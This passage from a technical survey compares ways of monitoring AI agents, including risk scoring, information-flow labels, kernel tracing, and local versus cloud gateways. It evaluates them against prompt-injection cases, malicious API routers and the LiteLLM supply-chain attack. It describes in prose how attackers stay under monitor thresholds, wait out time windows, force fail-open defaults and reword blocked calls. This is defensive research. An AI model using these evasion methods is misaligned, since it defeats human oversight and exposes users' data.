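           score     0.30   0.21   0.45   0.31   0.52   0.36   0.55
```

The hurried attack crosses the threshold at its third signal. The patient attack inserts a harmless step, such as reading an ordinary file, after each suspicious one, so its score stays below 0.30 / (1 − 0.7²), or about 0.59, however long it continues.

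Slower decay would catch the patient attacker but would also penalise long, honest sessions. With no decay, harmless steps that each scored 0.01 would reach 0.60 after 60 tool calls. FinHarness stops the decay only after a session has shown certain more serious warning signs. *SafeDream* (2026) instead subtracts the average score of harmless conversations at each step and never lets the total fall below zero. Ordinary conversations then stay near zero however long they last, but an attacker can still lower the total with harmless steps.

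Some monitors stop counting earlier events after a set time or when a session ends. *ClawSentry* (2026) counts recent high-risk events and, in its benchmark setting, drops those more than 300 seconds old. An attacker who can wait more than five minutes between steps would therefore have no earlier steps counted against the next one. PRISM clears a session's score when the session ends, so a false memory planted in one session would add nothing to the score of a later session in which the agent acts on it.

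Averaging the signals would be worse than any of these, because three signals of 0.30 would score the same as one. *Peak + Accumulation* (2026) therefore adds the highest signal to measures of how persistently signals occur and how many kinds there are. This method caught 90.8% of 588 attack conversations and flagged 1.20% of 10,066 harmless ones. But the attacks came from a collection of jailbreak prompts, so the result is weak evidence of how well the method would work on chains of tool calls. Like any formula for combining signals, it can't detect an attack whose individual steps produce none.

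### Labels on data

Information-flow control attaches labels to data and restricts what an agent may do with data that carries them. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, use two kinds of label. An integrity label records whether an outsider could have influenced the data, and a confidentiality label lists who may read it. In the ticket example, where a support agent publishes private facts about a bank in answer to a stranger's polite question, the labels would be:

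```
public ticket         untrusted    readers: everyone
export-cases.md       trusted      readers: staff
summary using both    untrusted    readers: staff
```

When data from two sources is combined, the result is labeled untrusted if either source is untrusted, and only people allowed to read both sources may read it.

A monitor can then enforce two general policies without understanding the text. The first allows a consequential action, such as a payment, only if nothing untrusted influenced the decision. The second allows the agent to send data only if every recipient is allowed to read it.

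A monitor can track data through an ordinary program by following each value from one variable to the next. Tracking data through a language model is harder, because the model computes every word of its output from the whole prompt, and the output doesn't show which parts of the prompt influenced it. To be safe, a monitor has to assume that all of them did. It therefore treats every decision an agent makes after reading a single untrusted page as untrusted, and a strict monitor blocks every consequential action for the rest of the session.

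To label responses more precisely, one method cited by Costa and colleagues identifies which messages influenced a response, then regenerates the response from those messages alone, so that it carries only their labels. CaMeL and FIDES, the two best-known designs, instead keep untrusted text away from the model that makes the decisions.

### CaMeL: plan first, read later

CaMeL, which Google DeepMind published in 2025, builds on an earlier proposal by Willison to use two models. As Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, explain, a privileged model reads only the user's request and writes a short program. A quarantined model, which has no tools, processes untrusted text when the program calls it. For the support agent, the program might be:

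```
ticket = read_ticket(812)
topic  = quarantined_model("Name the feature at fault", ticket)
cases  = search_files(topic)
reply  = quarantined_model("Draft an answer", ticket, cases)
post_reply(812, reply)
```

The privileged model writes these five lines before any model reads the ticket. Hostile text in the ticket can change the value of `topic` or `reply`, but it cannot add a line that emails the files to a stranger. CaMeL's interpreter runs the program, records the sources and permitted readers of every value, and applies a policy before each tool call.

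Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, tested CaMeL with newer models in systems where one agent delegates work to others. They switched off its data policies, so the tests measured only the protection from fixing the plan in advance. CaMeL reduced the average attack success rate across five models from 12.9% to 0.2%. The improvement came almost entirely from older models. Without CaMeL, no attacks succeeded against GPT-5.5 and only 1.5% succeeded against Claude Fable 5, though the attacks did not adapt to the model.

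The attacks that still succeeded exploited a gap in how agents communicated. In a demonstration with GPT-5.2, a user asked for a summary of job applicants to be sent to a colleague on Slack. The first two agents safely handled a hostile instruction in the applicant database as data. The coordinating agent then put the summary into its request to a third agent, which treated the whole request as coming from its user and emailed the summary to the attacker. Each agent had followed CaMeL's rules. Peters-Gill and colleagues closed the gap by sending instructions and data between agents separately, with the labels attached, after which no attack succeeded.

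Even without data policies, CaMeL lowered the success rate on AssetOpsBench, a set of multi-step professional tasks, by an average of 21.6 percentage points. For the two strongest models, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5, the average drop was 13.4 points. Separating instructions from data between agents lowered these two models' success rate by less than one additional point.

### FIDES: deciding along the way

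CaMeL has trouble with tasks where the next step depends on what the agent finds. FIDES, from Microsoft, lets its planning model choose one step at a time. When a tool returns untrusted text, FIDES stores the text in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name. The planner can pass the variable to another tool or have a quarantined model process it. It can also open the variable, but FIDES then treats the whole conversation as untrusted.

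A compromise is to give the planner very little information. Suppose a user asks the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and add any meeting to the calendar. The quarantined model can answer "is there a request?" with only yes or no. An attacker could make that answer wrong, but one bit is too small to contain an instruction, so a policy may allow the planner to act on the answer.

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. An ordinary agent fell for 152 attacks. With the policies enforced, none achieved a goal that the policies forbade. The cost appears in the share of tasks completed when nobody was attacking:

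| Agent | Office work | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no policies | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary agent, labels and policies enforced | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, labels and policies enforced | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

The second row gives the results when one untrusted message causes everything after it to be treated as untrusted. FIDES recovered part of the loss except on the travel tasks, where most actions were permitted anyway and GPT-4o struggled to use the variables. With o1, a stronger model, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks.

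The guarantee covers data that the agent copies or summarises, but not what an observer can infer from the agent's choices. If a ticket contains the request "please mark this as a duplicate if another customer has reported it", the agent's action reveals whether another customer has, even though it contains no private text. Costa and colleagues accepted this leak because preventing it would rule out almost every publicly visible action after the agent had read private data.

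### AGATE: authority and origin

CaMeL and FIDES are ways of building a harness, so a developer cannot add them to Codex or Claude Code by installing a proxy. AGATE attaches to existing harnesses through adapters. It evaluates each call with fixed checks, without using a language model, and it keeps permission to act separate from permission to send particular data.

Zhang and colleagues give the example of a maintenance guide that tells an agent to copy a "deployment check" from a file into a public DNS record. The "deployment check" is actually the server's API credential. The agent has permission to use both the tool that reads the file and the tool that updates DNS records, but that does not imply permission to publish what the first tool returned.

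Authority comes only from settings that the operator wrote outside the conversation, or from a real approval recorded by the harness. A sentence in a file such as "the user has already approved this" grants no authority. An approval applies to one session and to the exact arguments the person saw, so the agent needs a new approval if it changes the recipient of a payment. By default, an approval expires after 30 minutes or three uses. AGATE also triggers another review when the agent repeats an action on the same target.

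AGATE traces where data came from by storing fingerprints of 12-character fragments of the text that the agent reads. Before a call that crosses a protected boundary, it checks the outgoing fields for those fragments. AGATE does not have to track data through the model because it compares only what went in with what comes out. It may miss text that the model has reworded.

AGATE also holds the agent's edits to protected memory files as drafts until an operator approves them. That should stop an email from planting a false memory through the normal editing tools, but an agent might still change the file with a shell command.

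#### What the tests measured

The evaluation draws on 153 attack-chain records: 76 based on incidents and earlier studies, 49 that vary how the attack reaches the agent, and 28 that fill gaps in the collection. For each record, the researchers ran the chain and noted what happened, whether or not the attack succeeded. They ran the first 76 chains once on each of two harnesses without AGATE, for a baseline of 152 runs, but report no overall success rate for those runs.

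The paper does report results for the 49 delivery chains, again without AGATE. The attack succeeded in 12 of 46 runs when the text spelled it out, and in 23 of 52 when it was built into routine-looking instructions and files. The two groups used different tasks, so the wording may not explain the difference in success rates.

The 252 monitored runs covered 63 scenarios, each run twice on DeepSeek Harness, where AGATE could block calls, and twice on OpenCode, where it could only record them. Twelve scenarios involved business tools such as refunds. A call matching the tool and recipient the attacker wanted appeared in all 12 on OpenCode and in two on DeepSeek Harness. This 83% drop is not a block rate, because the instruction that carried the scenario's content into the agent's context reached OpenCode but not DeepSeek Harness, so some of the attacks may never have been attempted there. One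 of the two calls on DeepSeek Harness was also a legitimate message to the right person.

Later rounds on DeepSeek Harness give counts of refusals by how many tools the operator had approved:

| Tools approved in advance | Refused for lack of authority | Refused because of the data | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| 22 tools | 5 | 23 | 28 |
| Only those each scenario needed | 5 | 16 | 21 |
| None | 11 | 8 | 19 |

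These are individual refusals, and one attack can cause several, so they show that both checks take effect but not how many attacks AGATE prevented. With no tools approved, AGATE refused a refund that a forged memory file described as permanently authorised. Zhang and colleagues did not measure how much ordinary work the agent could still do with that setting.

In the clearest failure, an agent tried to delete a mailbox. AGATE refused the first call because its arguments matched untrusted text, but the agent rewrote the arguments and the second call reached the simulated deletion tool. Nobody had to design this evasion, because models often try another wording when they are blocked.

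False blocks were common. In six of 11 harmless file-processing scenarios, AGATE refused at least one call. Of the eight refusals, five blocked legitimate reuse of a file's contents, two came from mistaken file-name matches, and one correctly applied the configured rule. The researchers did not record whether the agent still finished those tasks. An earlier fix had removed four other false refusals by making AGATE ignore fields that only describe a command.

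Zhang and colleagues admit several other gaps. AGATE is designed to decode Base64 and similar disguises, but the tested version did not do so. They have not measured how much AGATE slows an agent or compared its checks with each other on the same harness. They also checked the wrong folder when testing whether an agent could tamper with AGATE's own files. They did confirm that replaying the stored log gave the same history in all 63 scenarios on both harnesses, which helps an investigator but doesn't prove that the log is complete.

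### AgentLoupe: labels in the kernel

AGATE's adapters record what passes through the harness. Bao, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *AgentLoupe*, attach labels further down, in the operating system's kernel, so that the labels can follow an action after it leaves the agent. Like AgentSight, their tool uses eBPF to read the agent's messages before encryption. Each new prompt gets a number, and the number spreads as follows:

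1. A program that the agent starts inherits the number.
2. When a labelled program writes a file, the kernel records the number against that file.
3. Any program that later opens or runs the file takes the number from it.
4. Network connections pass it on in a similar way.

In one test, an agent installed a scheduled job that would open a connection to an attacker an hour later. The system's scheduler, which the agent had not started, ran the job. AgentSight could not link the job to the agent because the job ran outside the agent's programs and long after the prompt. AgentLoupe traced a number from the prompt through the script and the scheduler to the network connection. In a second test, AgentLoupe linked a command in one session to an instruction that an earlier session had written into `AGENTS.md`, a file of standing instructions for coding agents.

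If every file passed on its number without limit, much of the computer might soon appear to depend on one prompt. To prevent this, AgentLoupe starts a new number for each independent prompt and keeps only a link to the old one. Bao and colleagues have not measured how often it still labels too much or too little, and these two cases are their only evidence that the tracing works. AgentLoupe slowed three tasks by 4.5% to 8.0%.

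AgentLoupe records actions but doesn't block them. Each of its labels is a number that identifies the prompt that led to an action. Unlike a FIDES label, it doesn't show whether the data involved was private. In the support agent's case, AgentLoupe could help an investigator find the prompt that led to the published reply, but only after the bank's plans were public.

### The ticket example under each method

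Unless the company bars the agent from reading private files while it handles public tickets, a tool policy would probably allow the whole chain, because the agent's job is to read files and answer tickets. The MCP proxy would make no difference, since the agent uses only permitted tools.

A risk score would do no better, because each step looks harmless and would probably score zero. Raising the score whenever the agent opened a private file would help, but that would be a crude way of taking the data's origin into account.

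Labels stop the leak because the reply is based on `export-cases.md`, which only staff may read, and anyone can read the ticket site. If the same facts had come from a press release, the label would allow an identical reply. The protection depends on someone having labelled the file correctly. It would also block a harmless reply, such as one that said only "please install the latest version", if the agent had drawn on the file to write it.

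To find a match, AGATE would need a piece of the original text to appear in the reply. "Northwind Bank" has 14 characters, so if the name appears in both the file and the reply, a 12-character fragment could match. If the agent wrote "another bank" instead, AGATE would probably find nothing. It also stores at most 512 fragments each time it registers a text, which may leave part of a long file uncovered.

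An employee could settle the doubtful cases. In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) suggest that approval requests show where the data came from. A box with the text "this public reply uses `export-cases.md`" would help an employee who didn't know that the bank's move was confidential.

### Do policies cost too much?

The main objection to these methods is that their policies take a lot of work to write and then stop the agent from doing its job. Someone has to decide which tools each role needs, who may read each file and which sources to trust. CaMeL also needs an exact description of what every tool returns, because the privileged model writes its program before seeing any results. Peters-Gill and colleagues consider this a modest, one-time job, but a company that keeps adding tools will have to repeat it for each new one.

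FIDES with GPT-4o completed about half of the banking and Slack tasks, compared with over 90% for an unprotected agent. Those two areas have the largest shares of tasks in which the next step depends on what the agent has read, at 43.8% for banking and 42.9% for Slack, compared with only 5% for office tasks. A user who asks an agent to "pay the bill in this file" wants the file to influence the payment, which a strict integrity policy forbids.

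Kolluri and colleagues reply that this comparison is unfair. Many real agents already stop and ask a person before consequential actions, so the sensible comparison is with an agent that asks every time. They built PRUDENTIA, a version of FIDES that tells the planner about the policies so that it can plan around them. On AgentDojo with GPT-5, the results were:

| Agent | Tasks completed without asking | Tasks completed with approvals | Approvals needed in total |
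|---|---|---|---|
| Asks before every consequential action | 35.1% | 72.3% | 52.0 |
| Same agent, asks only when labels require it | 43.4% | 72.3% | 40.4 |
| FIDES | 57.1% | 78.9% | 41.3 |
| PRUDENTIA | 72.7% | 80.0% | 7.3 |

PRUDENTIA completed more tasks than the agent that always asked, and it needed about a seventh as many approvals. With fewer requests, people should also read each one more carefully. PRUDENTIA needs fewer approvals partly because users can approve data instead of individual actions. If an email contains ten chores, the user can declare the email trustworthy once and the agent can do all ten. But if the user overlooks an instruction hidden in the email, they have approved that too.

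Because of the extra planning, PRUDENTIA with GPT-4o cost roughly four to ten times as much per task as a simple agent with labels, though still only a few cents. Kolluri and colleagues had not tried to reduce this cost.

Better tools may also make policies easier to write and reduce the work lost to late refusals. Nikolaou and colleagues extended CaMeL with a checker that examines the whole program before it runs. For example, a security team can require an agent to get approval before disconnecting a computer from the network. If a plan omits the approval, the checker returns the offending sequence and the model revises the plan. CaMeL alone would detect the problem only at the last step. A language model can translate such rules from ordinary English, but a person still has to check the translation.

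On this evidence, the objection is strong for older models and for agents that must act on what strangers write, and weaker for capable models doing predictable office work. Coding agents are likely to be a hard case, and AgentDojo has no coding suite. The failing-build agent reads an untrusted log and chooses its next command based on it. A strict integrity policy would require the developer to approve every consequential command after that. The practical alternative is to limit what the commands can affect, for instance by running the build in an isolated environment that contains no real passwords and cannot reach the internet.

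## Local monitor or cloud gateway: whom each asks you to trust

The case for running a monitor on the developer's own machine, and not at a remote service, rests on four premises:

1. A cloud gateway has to hold the text in readable form to inspect it.
2. Every additional party that holds the text adds risk.
3. A local monitor adds no remote party.
4. A local monitor protects the agent as well as a gateway would.

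The evidence for the first two is good, though the added risk depends heavily on who runs the gateway. The last two often fail in practice because many monitors that run beside the agent send text to the cloud, and a monitor on the agent's own machine is easier to switch off.

### A gateway that can read messages can change them

A gateway has to decrypt traffic in both directions to inspect it, so its operator can also alter a tool call on the way to the harness.

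Model providers could make such changes detectable by signing their responses, much as email services sign messages. *Your Agent Has a Middleman You Didn't Vet* (Crosley, 2026) reports that researchers who studied routers proposed this but found no major provider that did it. Signing would not prevent the theft of secrets, since the operator can read them in the request before the provider signs a response.

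The developer may not know how many operators there are. In an example Crosley takes from the same research, a developer buys access from a reseller, which buys it from an aggregator. The aggregator uses the commercial router OpenRouter, which passes the request to the company that hosts the model. All four can read everything, but the developer has configured only the reseller's address.

### 428 routers from informal markets

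In *Your Agent Is Mine*, Liu, Shou and colleagues (2026) bought access to 28 routers from the Chinese marketplaces Taobao and Xianyu and from shops hosted on Shopify, and collected 400 free ones from public communities. They ran a coding agent through each router in an isolated environment, executed every tool call that came back, and watched for unexpected connections, file changes and new processes. They also planted Amazon Web Services (AWS) credentials and a cryptocurrency wallet key to see whether anyone would use them.

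| Behaviour | Paid routers (28) | Free routers (400) |
|---|---|---|
| Inserted malicious code into tool calls | 1 | 8 |
| Did so only when a hidden condition was met | 0 | 2 |
| Passed on an AWS credential that someone then used | 0 | 17 |
| Passed on a wallet key that someone then used to take the money | 0 | 1 |

One of the two routers with hidden conditions did nothing malicious for the first 50 requests. The other attacked only projects written in Rust or Go, and only when the agent seemed to be running commands without asking for approval. A short test would have detected neither, so the researchers may have missed other malicious routers in the sample.

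The rate of about 2% (nine in 428) doesn't apply to gateways in general. Most of the routers came from Chinese-language markets and communities, two open-source templates dominated the free ones, and the researchers left out enterprise and invitation-only services. A company that runs its own gateway knows who operates it, can inspect its code and can pay the model provider directly, so it avoids the main danger in this sample, an anonymous seller with an incentive to steal. The sample of paid routers is also too small to show whether paying for access helps. One of the 28 was malicious, so the true share could be anywhere from about 0.1% to 18%.

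An honest operator can still expose its users if its relay is poorly secured. Liu and colleagues set up decoy relays with weak passwords or known flaws on 20 domains and 20 internet addresses. Strangers made more than 40,000 unauthorised access attempts, and the decoys were soon carrying other people's agent traffic. The researchers could have read 99 credentials in 440 Codex sessions, and in 401 of those sessions the agent ran commands without asking for approval. The developers could not have known that their requests were passing through a stranger's server. This part of the study is relevant to company gateways because it shows how quickly outsiders find and use a badly protected one.

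### What a tampered response does to a coding agent

The router study showed that some operators rewrite tool calls, but it did not show what happens next in a real coding agent. *Where Is the Cost of Third-Party API Routers in Agentic Software Development?* tested this in July 2026 with Claude Code, Codex, Cursor and OpenCode. The researchers wrote 400 malicious tool calls, 100 each for running hostile code, inserting bugs, stealing private data and tampering with the software supply chain. They recorded the agents working on three real programming tasks, replayed the recordings through a router they controlled, and had the router insert one malicious call in each run.

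None of the four agents blocked any calls under any setting tested. Claude Code's plan mode, which is meant to be read-only, didn't help because it restricts the agent through instructions to the model, and the router changed the response after the model had written it. Some settings have a second model review risky actions, but the review requests went through the same router. The researchers didn't test Claude Code's default mode, in which a person approves commands, so the result doesn't cover developers who read each one.

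The attacks were also hard to notice from the results. When the router replaced a response with a malicious call, the share of tasks Claude Code completed fell by less than one percentage point with two DeepSeek models and by about seven points with models from Kimi and Qwen.

The researchers then added two defences to Claude Code. An allowlist permitted only known web domains and software packages, and a separate model reviewed each call over a direct connection that avoided the router. The table gives the share of malicious calls that each defence stopped:

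| What the router did | Allowlist | Reviewing model (range over four models) |
|---|---|---|
| Replaced the response with a malicious call | 34.9% | 49.9–64.4% |
| Added a malicious call to the response | 44.1% | 40.3–51.1% |
| Added the call and rewrote the explanation to match | 31.1% | 41.5–51.8% |
| Regenerated the whole response so that the call fitted in | 30.8% | 39.1–50.8% |

Liu and colleagues got a far better result from a similar allowlist, which blocked every malicious command in their own test and only 1% of harmless ones. But their attacks all fetched something from an unlisted domain or installed an unlisted package, which is what such a list detects. The list can't detect a bug written into a source file. When they assumed an attacker who knew about the list and hosted the hostile code on a permitted domain, every attack got through.

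A local monitor between the router and the harness can stop some tampering, but it cannot compare the response it receives with the original. The surest protection is to connect directly to the model provider.

### LiteLLM: a gateway that companies run themselves

LiteLLM is an open-source router that many companies run on their own servers. On 24 March 2026, attackers published two malicious versions of it on PyPI, the main public collection of Python packages. LiteLLM's chief executive and chief technology officer, Dholakia and Jaff (2026), in *Security Townhall Updates*, trace the attack to Trivy, a security scanner that LiteLLM used to check its own code. It happened in three steps:

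1. The attackers compromised Trivy. LiteLLM's build system had not fixed which version of Trivy to use, so it ran the compromised one.
2. The scanner shared an environment with LiteLLM's publishing credentials, which the attackers stole.
3. They used the credentials to upload their own versions straight to PyPI, without touching LiteLLM's source code.

According to LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026), the malicious versions searched the computer for cloud credentials, database passwords and other secrets, then sent them to a web address that resembled LiteLLM's own. Willison notes in *Malicious litellm_init.pth in litellm 1.82.8* (2026) that installing the second version was enough to start the theft, while the first version started it only when a program loaded it.

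PyPI quarantined the packages after about 40 minutes. heise's *Supply chain attack on LiteLLM* (2026) called estimates of several hundred thousand affected systems realistic, based on 3.4 million downloads a day and a window of more than five hours. At that rate, there would be about 94,000 downloads in 40 minutes. That figure would include downloads of older, safe versions, so the number of affected systems was probably lower.

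This incident is at least as much a warning about local software as about malicious gateways, though people sometimes cite it as an example of the latter. LiteLLM reported that the incident did not affect customers of its cloud service or users of its official container image, which fixed the exact version of every package. Those at risk had installed the package themselves. A local monitor is also a package that someone installs, usually with access to the secrets it is supposed to protect. Security tools can be compromised too. Help Net Security's *LiteLLM PyPI packages compromised in expanding TeamPCP supply chain attacks* reports that the group believed to be responsible had also compromised plug-ins from Checkmarx, another security company, the day before.

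A gateway adds its own risk because it holds a whole company's keys in one place. Crosley describes a flaw that LiteLLM fixed in August 2026. Anyone with an account on a company's LiteLLM proxy could make it send the company's model-provider credentials to a server of their choice. A similar flaw in a monitor on one laptop would have exposed only one developer's credentials.

### Monitors that run locally and send the text away

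Cisco sells a software library that, like Akto's sidecar, monitors an agent locally but sends text elsewhere for a verdict. The library runs inside the agent's own process and inspects every message to a model or an MCP tool. Cisco says the library sends this content to its AI Defense service. In one mode, all the agent's traffic passes through Cisco's gateway. In the other, the agent contacts the model provider directly after the inspection, so Cisco cannot rewrite a tool call in transit, but its service still receives the text.

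Other products run some checks locally and others in the cloud. Arcjet's *Keeping Security Inspection Local So Data Stays in Your Environment* lists where each of the company's checks runs. The check for card numbers, email addresses and other personal data runs inside the customer's application and sends none of the content out. The check for prompt injection sends the whole prompt to Arcjet's cloud because it uses a specialised model there. A customer who bought the product to keep prompts private would have to leave that check switched off.

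Injection detection can also run locally. Horizon-Labs's classifier, which did well on agents' tool results in the tests described earlier, is small enough to run on a laptop. To test any vendor's claim that its monitor runs locally, Arcjet suggests recording the application's network traffic and checking whether the monitor still works when it can't reach the vendor.

Even if a monitor sends nothing to its maker, the model provider still receives any sensitive text the monitor doesn't remove first. In the failing build, a local monitor that only displayed a warning would let the database password reach the provider.

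| Where the inspection happens | Outside companies that receive readable text |
|---|---|
| Entirely on the laptop | Model provider |
| On the laptop, with a cloud classifier | Model provider and classifier company |
| At a gateway on the company's own servers | Model provider |
| At a vendor's cloud gateway | Model provider and gateway vendor |

For a company that uses a cloud model, inspecting data locally or through a gateway on its own servers therefore reduces the number of outside parties that hold its data from two to one. This is useful, but it protects the company much less than keeping the data private would.

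The difference can matter legally even when the practical risk is small. Under the EU's data protection law, a vendor that receives personal data to inspect it needs a formal agreement with the customer, and any transfer abroad needs a legal basis. Arcjet, which has an interest in the argument, points out that a vendor's promise not to store the data doesn't satisfy a rule against transferring it. A hospital might choose local inspection for this reason alone.

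### Does a local monitor protect as well?

An extra holder adds risk, but a good monitor also removes some. Suppose that a company has a 6% chance each year of a serious leak through its agents, and that a cloud gateway has a 1% chance of a breach that would be just as serious. These figures are invented, but they show what the choice depends on:

```
no monitor                                                6.0%
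gateway that prevents half the leaks    1 − 0.97 × 0.99 = 4.0%
local monitor that prevents half        6% × 1/2        = 3.0%
local monitor that prevents a third     6% × 2/3        = 4.0%
```

The local monitor is clearly better if it works as well as the cloud gateway. If it prevents only a third of the leaks, it loses this advantage, even before counting the chance that someone attacks the monitor.

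A local monitor is faster for simple checks. Arcjet says its local analysis adds less than a millisecond, while a remote service adds a trip across the network. A developer would rarely notice the difference, because a call to the model takes a second or more. For checks that need a language model, a laptop may well be slower than a remote service. OpenClaw PRISM's local judge, for example, sometimes hit its 20-second time limit.

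A local monitor's ability to work offline helps only if the agent's model is also local, because an agent with a remote model stops when the connection drops. However, a local monitor keeps working when the security vendor has an outage.

A gateway is easier to manage because when a new kind of attack appears, a security team can change one rule to cover every agent whose traffic passes through it. Arcjet concedes that its local detection rules ship with the customer's application, so updating them means releasing a new version. It also concedes that models small enough to run locally are generally less accurate than those a vendor can run on its servers.

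A gateway can also compare the traffic of many agents. If the same strange sentence arrives in a thousand employees' inboxes, a gateway can detect the repetition, but a local monitor that checks only one inbox can't. Local monitors could share short codes computed from suspicious texts instead of the texts themselves, but an attacker could defeat exact matching by varying a few words in each email. The vendors' case for shared detection is plausible, but it would be much stronger with measurements of how many more attacks this method catches.

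### Switching off a monitor, or going around it

A local monitor and the agent's commands usually run under the same account, the developer's. An injected instruction could therefore make the agent stop the monitor's process, edit its rules or remove the setting that directs the harness to the monitor. A malicious package in the build could do the same without involving the model. Running the monitor under a separate account and locking its settings would prevent the simplest versions of these attacks.

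Those commands can't reach a gateway on another machine, but the agent may still be able to bypass it. If the laptop can connect directly to the model provider or to an attacker's server, that traffic never passes through the gateway. The gateway's resistance to tampering therefore helps only to the extent that network rules block other routes.

Those rules can fail when the monitor is a sidecar. On Kubernetes, the container-management system, an agent and its sidecar normally share a pod, a group of containers with a single network address. According to Kubernetes' *Network Policies*, its network rules apply to a whole pod. If they let the sidecar connect to the model provider, the agent can also connect directly. The rules also can't block the loopback interface, which programs in the same pod use to reach one another.

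Entuit's *Securing Self-Hosted LLMs and AI Agents on Kubernetes* describes a design in which a company runs its own model and wants every request to pass an identity check. It rejects a sidecar because the sidecar would reach the model over loopback, so no network rule could guarantee that requests came only through the check. Entuit puts the check in a separate pod and allows only that pod to connect to the model. It also limits the pods in which agents run commands to four destinations: the gateway, two internal databases and the DNS server.

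That would stop an agent from opening a connection to an attacker's website, but it might not stop a password from leaving inside a DNS lookup. According to Kubernetes, its network rules also do nothing unless the installed networking software enforces them.

A gateway like Entuit's is remote from the agent but belongs to the company, so it resists tampering by the agent without giving the text to another outside company. It is probably a better choice than a sidecar or a vendor's cloud for an organisation with the staff to run it. An individual developer can get some of the same benefit by running the agent in a virtual machine and the monitor outside it.

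### Attacking the monitor itself

A monitor that reads everything an agent sends is a valuable target for attackers. A proxy that decrypts traffic by impersonating the provider, as PIsberg's firewall does, keeps the private key of a certificate authority that the laptop trusts. Unless that authority is restricted to certain domain names, anyone who stole the key could create a certificate for the developer's bank that the laptop would accept. The thief would still have to intercept the connection, for instance on a shared wireless network. Directing the harness to a local address avoids this problem because it needs no certificate.

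The monitor's logs are another risk. A monitor that stored every resent conversation in full would soon have dozens of copies of the same password. Logs can still help after an attack by showing which sessions a bad router handled. Crosley recommends removing secrets before writing the log and keeping it where the router can't reach it.

A local proxy also has to open a port, a numbered entry point for connections. If the proxy adds the developer's credential to each request, any program on the laptop that can reach the port may be able to use the developer's account. If the proxy also accepts connections from other machines, strangers on the same network may be able to use the account too.

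A monitor's designer must also choose whether it "fails open", letting traffic through when the monitor fails, or "fails closed", blocking it. Microsoft's Copilot Studio, a tool for building agents, can ask an outside security service to approve each tool call. It sends the service the user's prompt, recent messages, earlier tool results and the proposed call. Microsoft says that if the service doesn't answer within one second, the agent goes ahead with the call unless an administrator has chosen to block it. Under that default, an attacker who could slow the service down, perhaps with very long inputs, could get a call through without fooling it. Judges as slow as PRISM's would often miss such a deadline even without an attack.

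A monitor that fails closed stops the agent during every outage, and developers who lose an afternoon's work that way may turn the monitor off permanently. A reasonable compromise is to fail closed for actions that are dangerous or hard to undo, such as sending data to a new address, and to fail open for reading a project's files.

Some failures produce no error. Crosley cites a warning in Claude Code's documentation that a mistyped path in the settings file leaves a hook "silently disabled". The developer would believe that the monitor was approving every command when it had never run. Testing it with a harmless command that it should refuse would reveal the failure.

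### Flaws in the agent's own program

A monitor that runs inside the harness also depends on the harness's code. *Local LLM Agents as Vulnerable Runtimes* (Zhang, Li and colleagues, 2026) examined this code in OpenClaw, the personal assistant that PRISM protects. OpenClaw's developers published 602 security advisories between 31 January and 15 May 2026, and the researchers recovered the faulty source code for 446 of them. They found that 146 of these were of high or critical severity. The most common type, with 77 cases, was a permission check that an attacker could bypass.

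Every part of OpenClaw runs with the full permissions of the user who started it, so a mistake in the part that loads skills can expose the same files and credentials as a mistake in the part that checks permissions. No internal barrier contains the damage or protects a plug-in monitor running in the same process. The many advisories partly reflect how many people were searching a popular program for flaws, so they don't show that OpenClaw is less secure than closed-source agents.

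Zhang and colleagues also tested whether automated tools could find such flaws. They wrote rules for two code scanners based on the 229 advisories published before April, then tried them on the 217 that came later:

| Scanner | Later flaws found with standard rules | With the researchers' rules added |
|---|---|---|
| Semgrep | 21.7% | 66.8% |
| CodeQL | 13.8% | 75.1% |

The improvement is large, but the test was lenient. It counted a flaw as found if the scanner flagged anything in a file that the developers later changed to fix it. When the researchers ran their rules on OpenClaw's current code and checked 50 of the warnings by hand, only six, or about one in eight, were real problems.

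The audit covered agents, not monitors. But a monitor does much of the same work, such as interpreting text from strangers and deciding which actions to permit, and there is no obvious reason to expect fewer mistakes in its code.

### A gateway whose operator cannot read the text

The premise that a gateway must hold readable text has an important exception. Xie and colleagues built a router in which the text is readable only inside an enclave, a part of a computer that the hardware seals off from the machine's owner. A sidecar on the user's machine checks the enclave before sending it anything:

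1. The operator publishes the source code of the program that will run in the enclave, with a signed record in a public log.
2. The user, or the user's coding agent, reviews the code and builds it. The build produces a measurement, a short code that identifies that exact program.
3. At the start of a session, the sidecar asks the enclave for proof of what it is running. The hardware signs this proof, which includes the measurement and the certificate for the connection.
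4. If everything matches, the sidecar encrypts the request so that only the enclave can read it. If anything doesn't match, it sends nothing.
5. The enclave forwards the request unchanged to a provider on a fixed list, and returns the response unchanged.

The operator's ordinary software still handles accounts and billing but receives only encrypted text and usage figures. In tests, the operator could not rewrite tool calls or search the traffic for secrets, though both attacks worked on an ordinary router.

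The protection adds little delay. For small requests, the router added a median of 5.7 milliseconds, 3.7 of which it would have added even without the enclave. The delay grew to 52 milliseconds for a one-megabyte request, a size that a long coding session might reach. Opening a session took another 12 milliseconds.

The user still has to trust several parties. The model provider still receives the full text. The enclave depends on Amazon's hardware, and Xie and colleagues exclude physical attacks on that hardware from their guarantee. Someone also has to review the enclave's program well enough to notice a hidden fault. The program has only 851 lines. When the researchers planted ten faults in a small test version, Codex found eight and Claude Code found all ten. This is encouraging, but a malicious operator would hide a fault more carefully than a researcher preparing a test.

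The operator also sees the size and timing of each message, which can reveal something about the contents. It can exploit this more easily than a network eavesdropper because it handles every connection and can send its own messages through the router for comparison. It can also refuse to deliver a request.

The enclave inspects nothing, which is the design's biggest limitation as an answer to the local-or-cloud question. If a web page hijacks the model, the enclave delivers the resulting tool call unchanged, like any other. Adding detection to the enclave would give users more code to review. Xie and colleagues counted 1,236 lines in their program and, by the same method, 10,434 in the nearest comparable gateway, which also selects providers and handles payments inside its enclave.

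The sidecar could inspect requests instead. It already handles each request on the laptop before encrypting it, so it could first replace the database password with a placeholder. The router's operator could not read the encrypted request, and the model provider would never receive the password. Xie and colleagues did not build this, and their sidecar would need protection from the agent's own commands, as any local monitor does.
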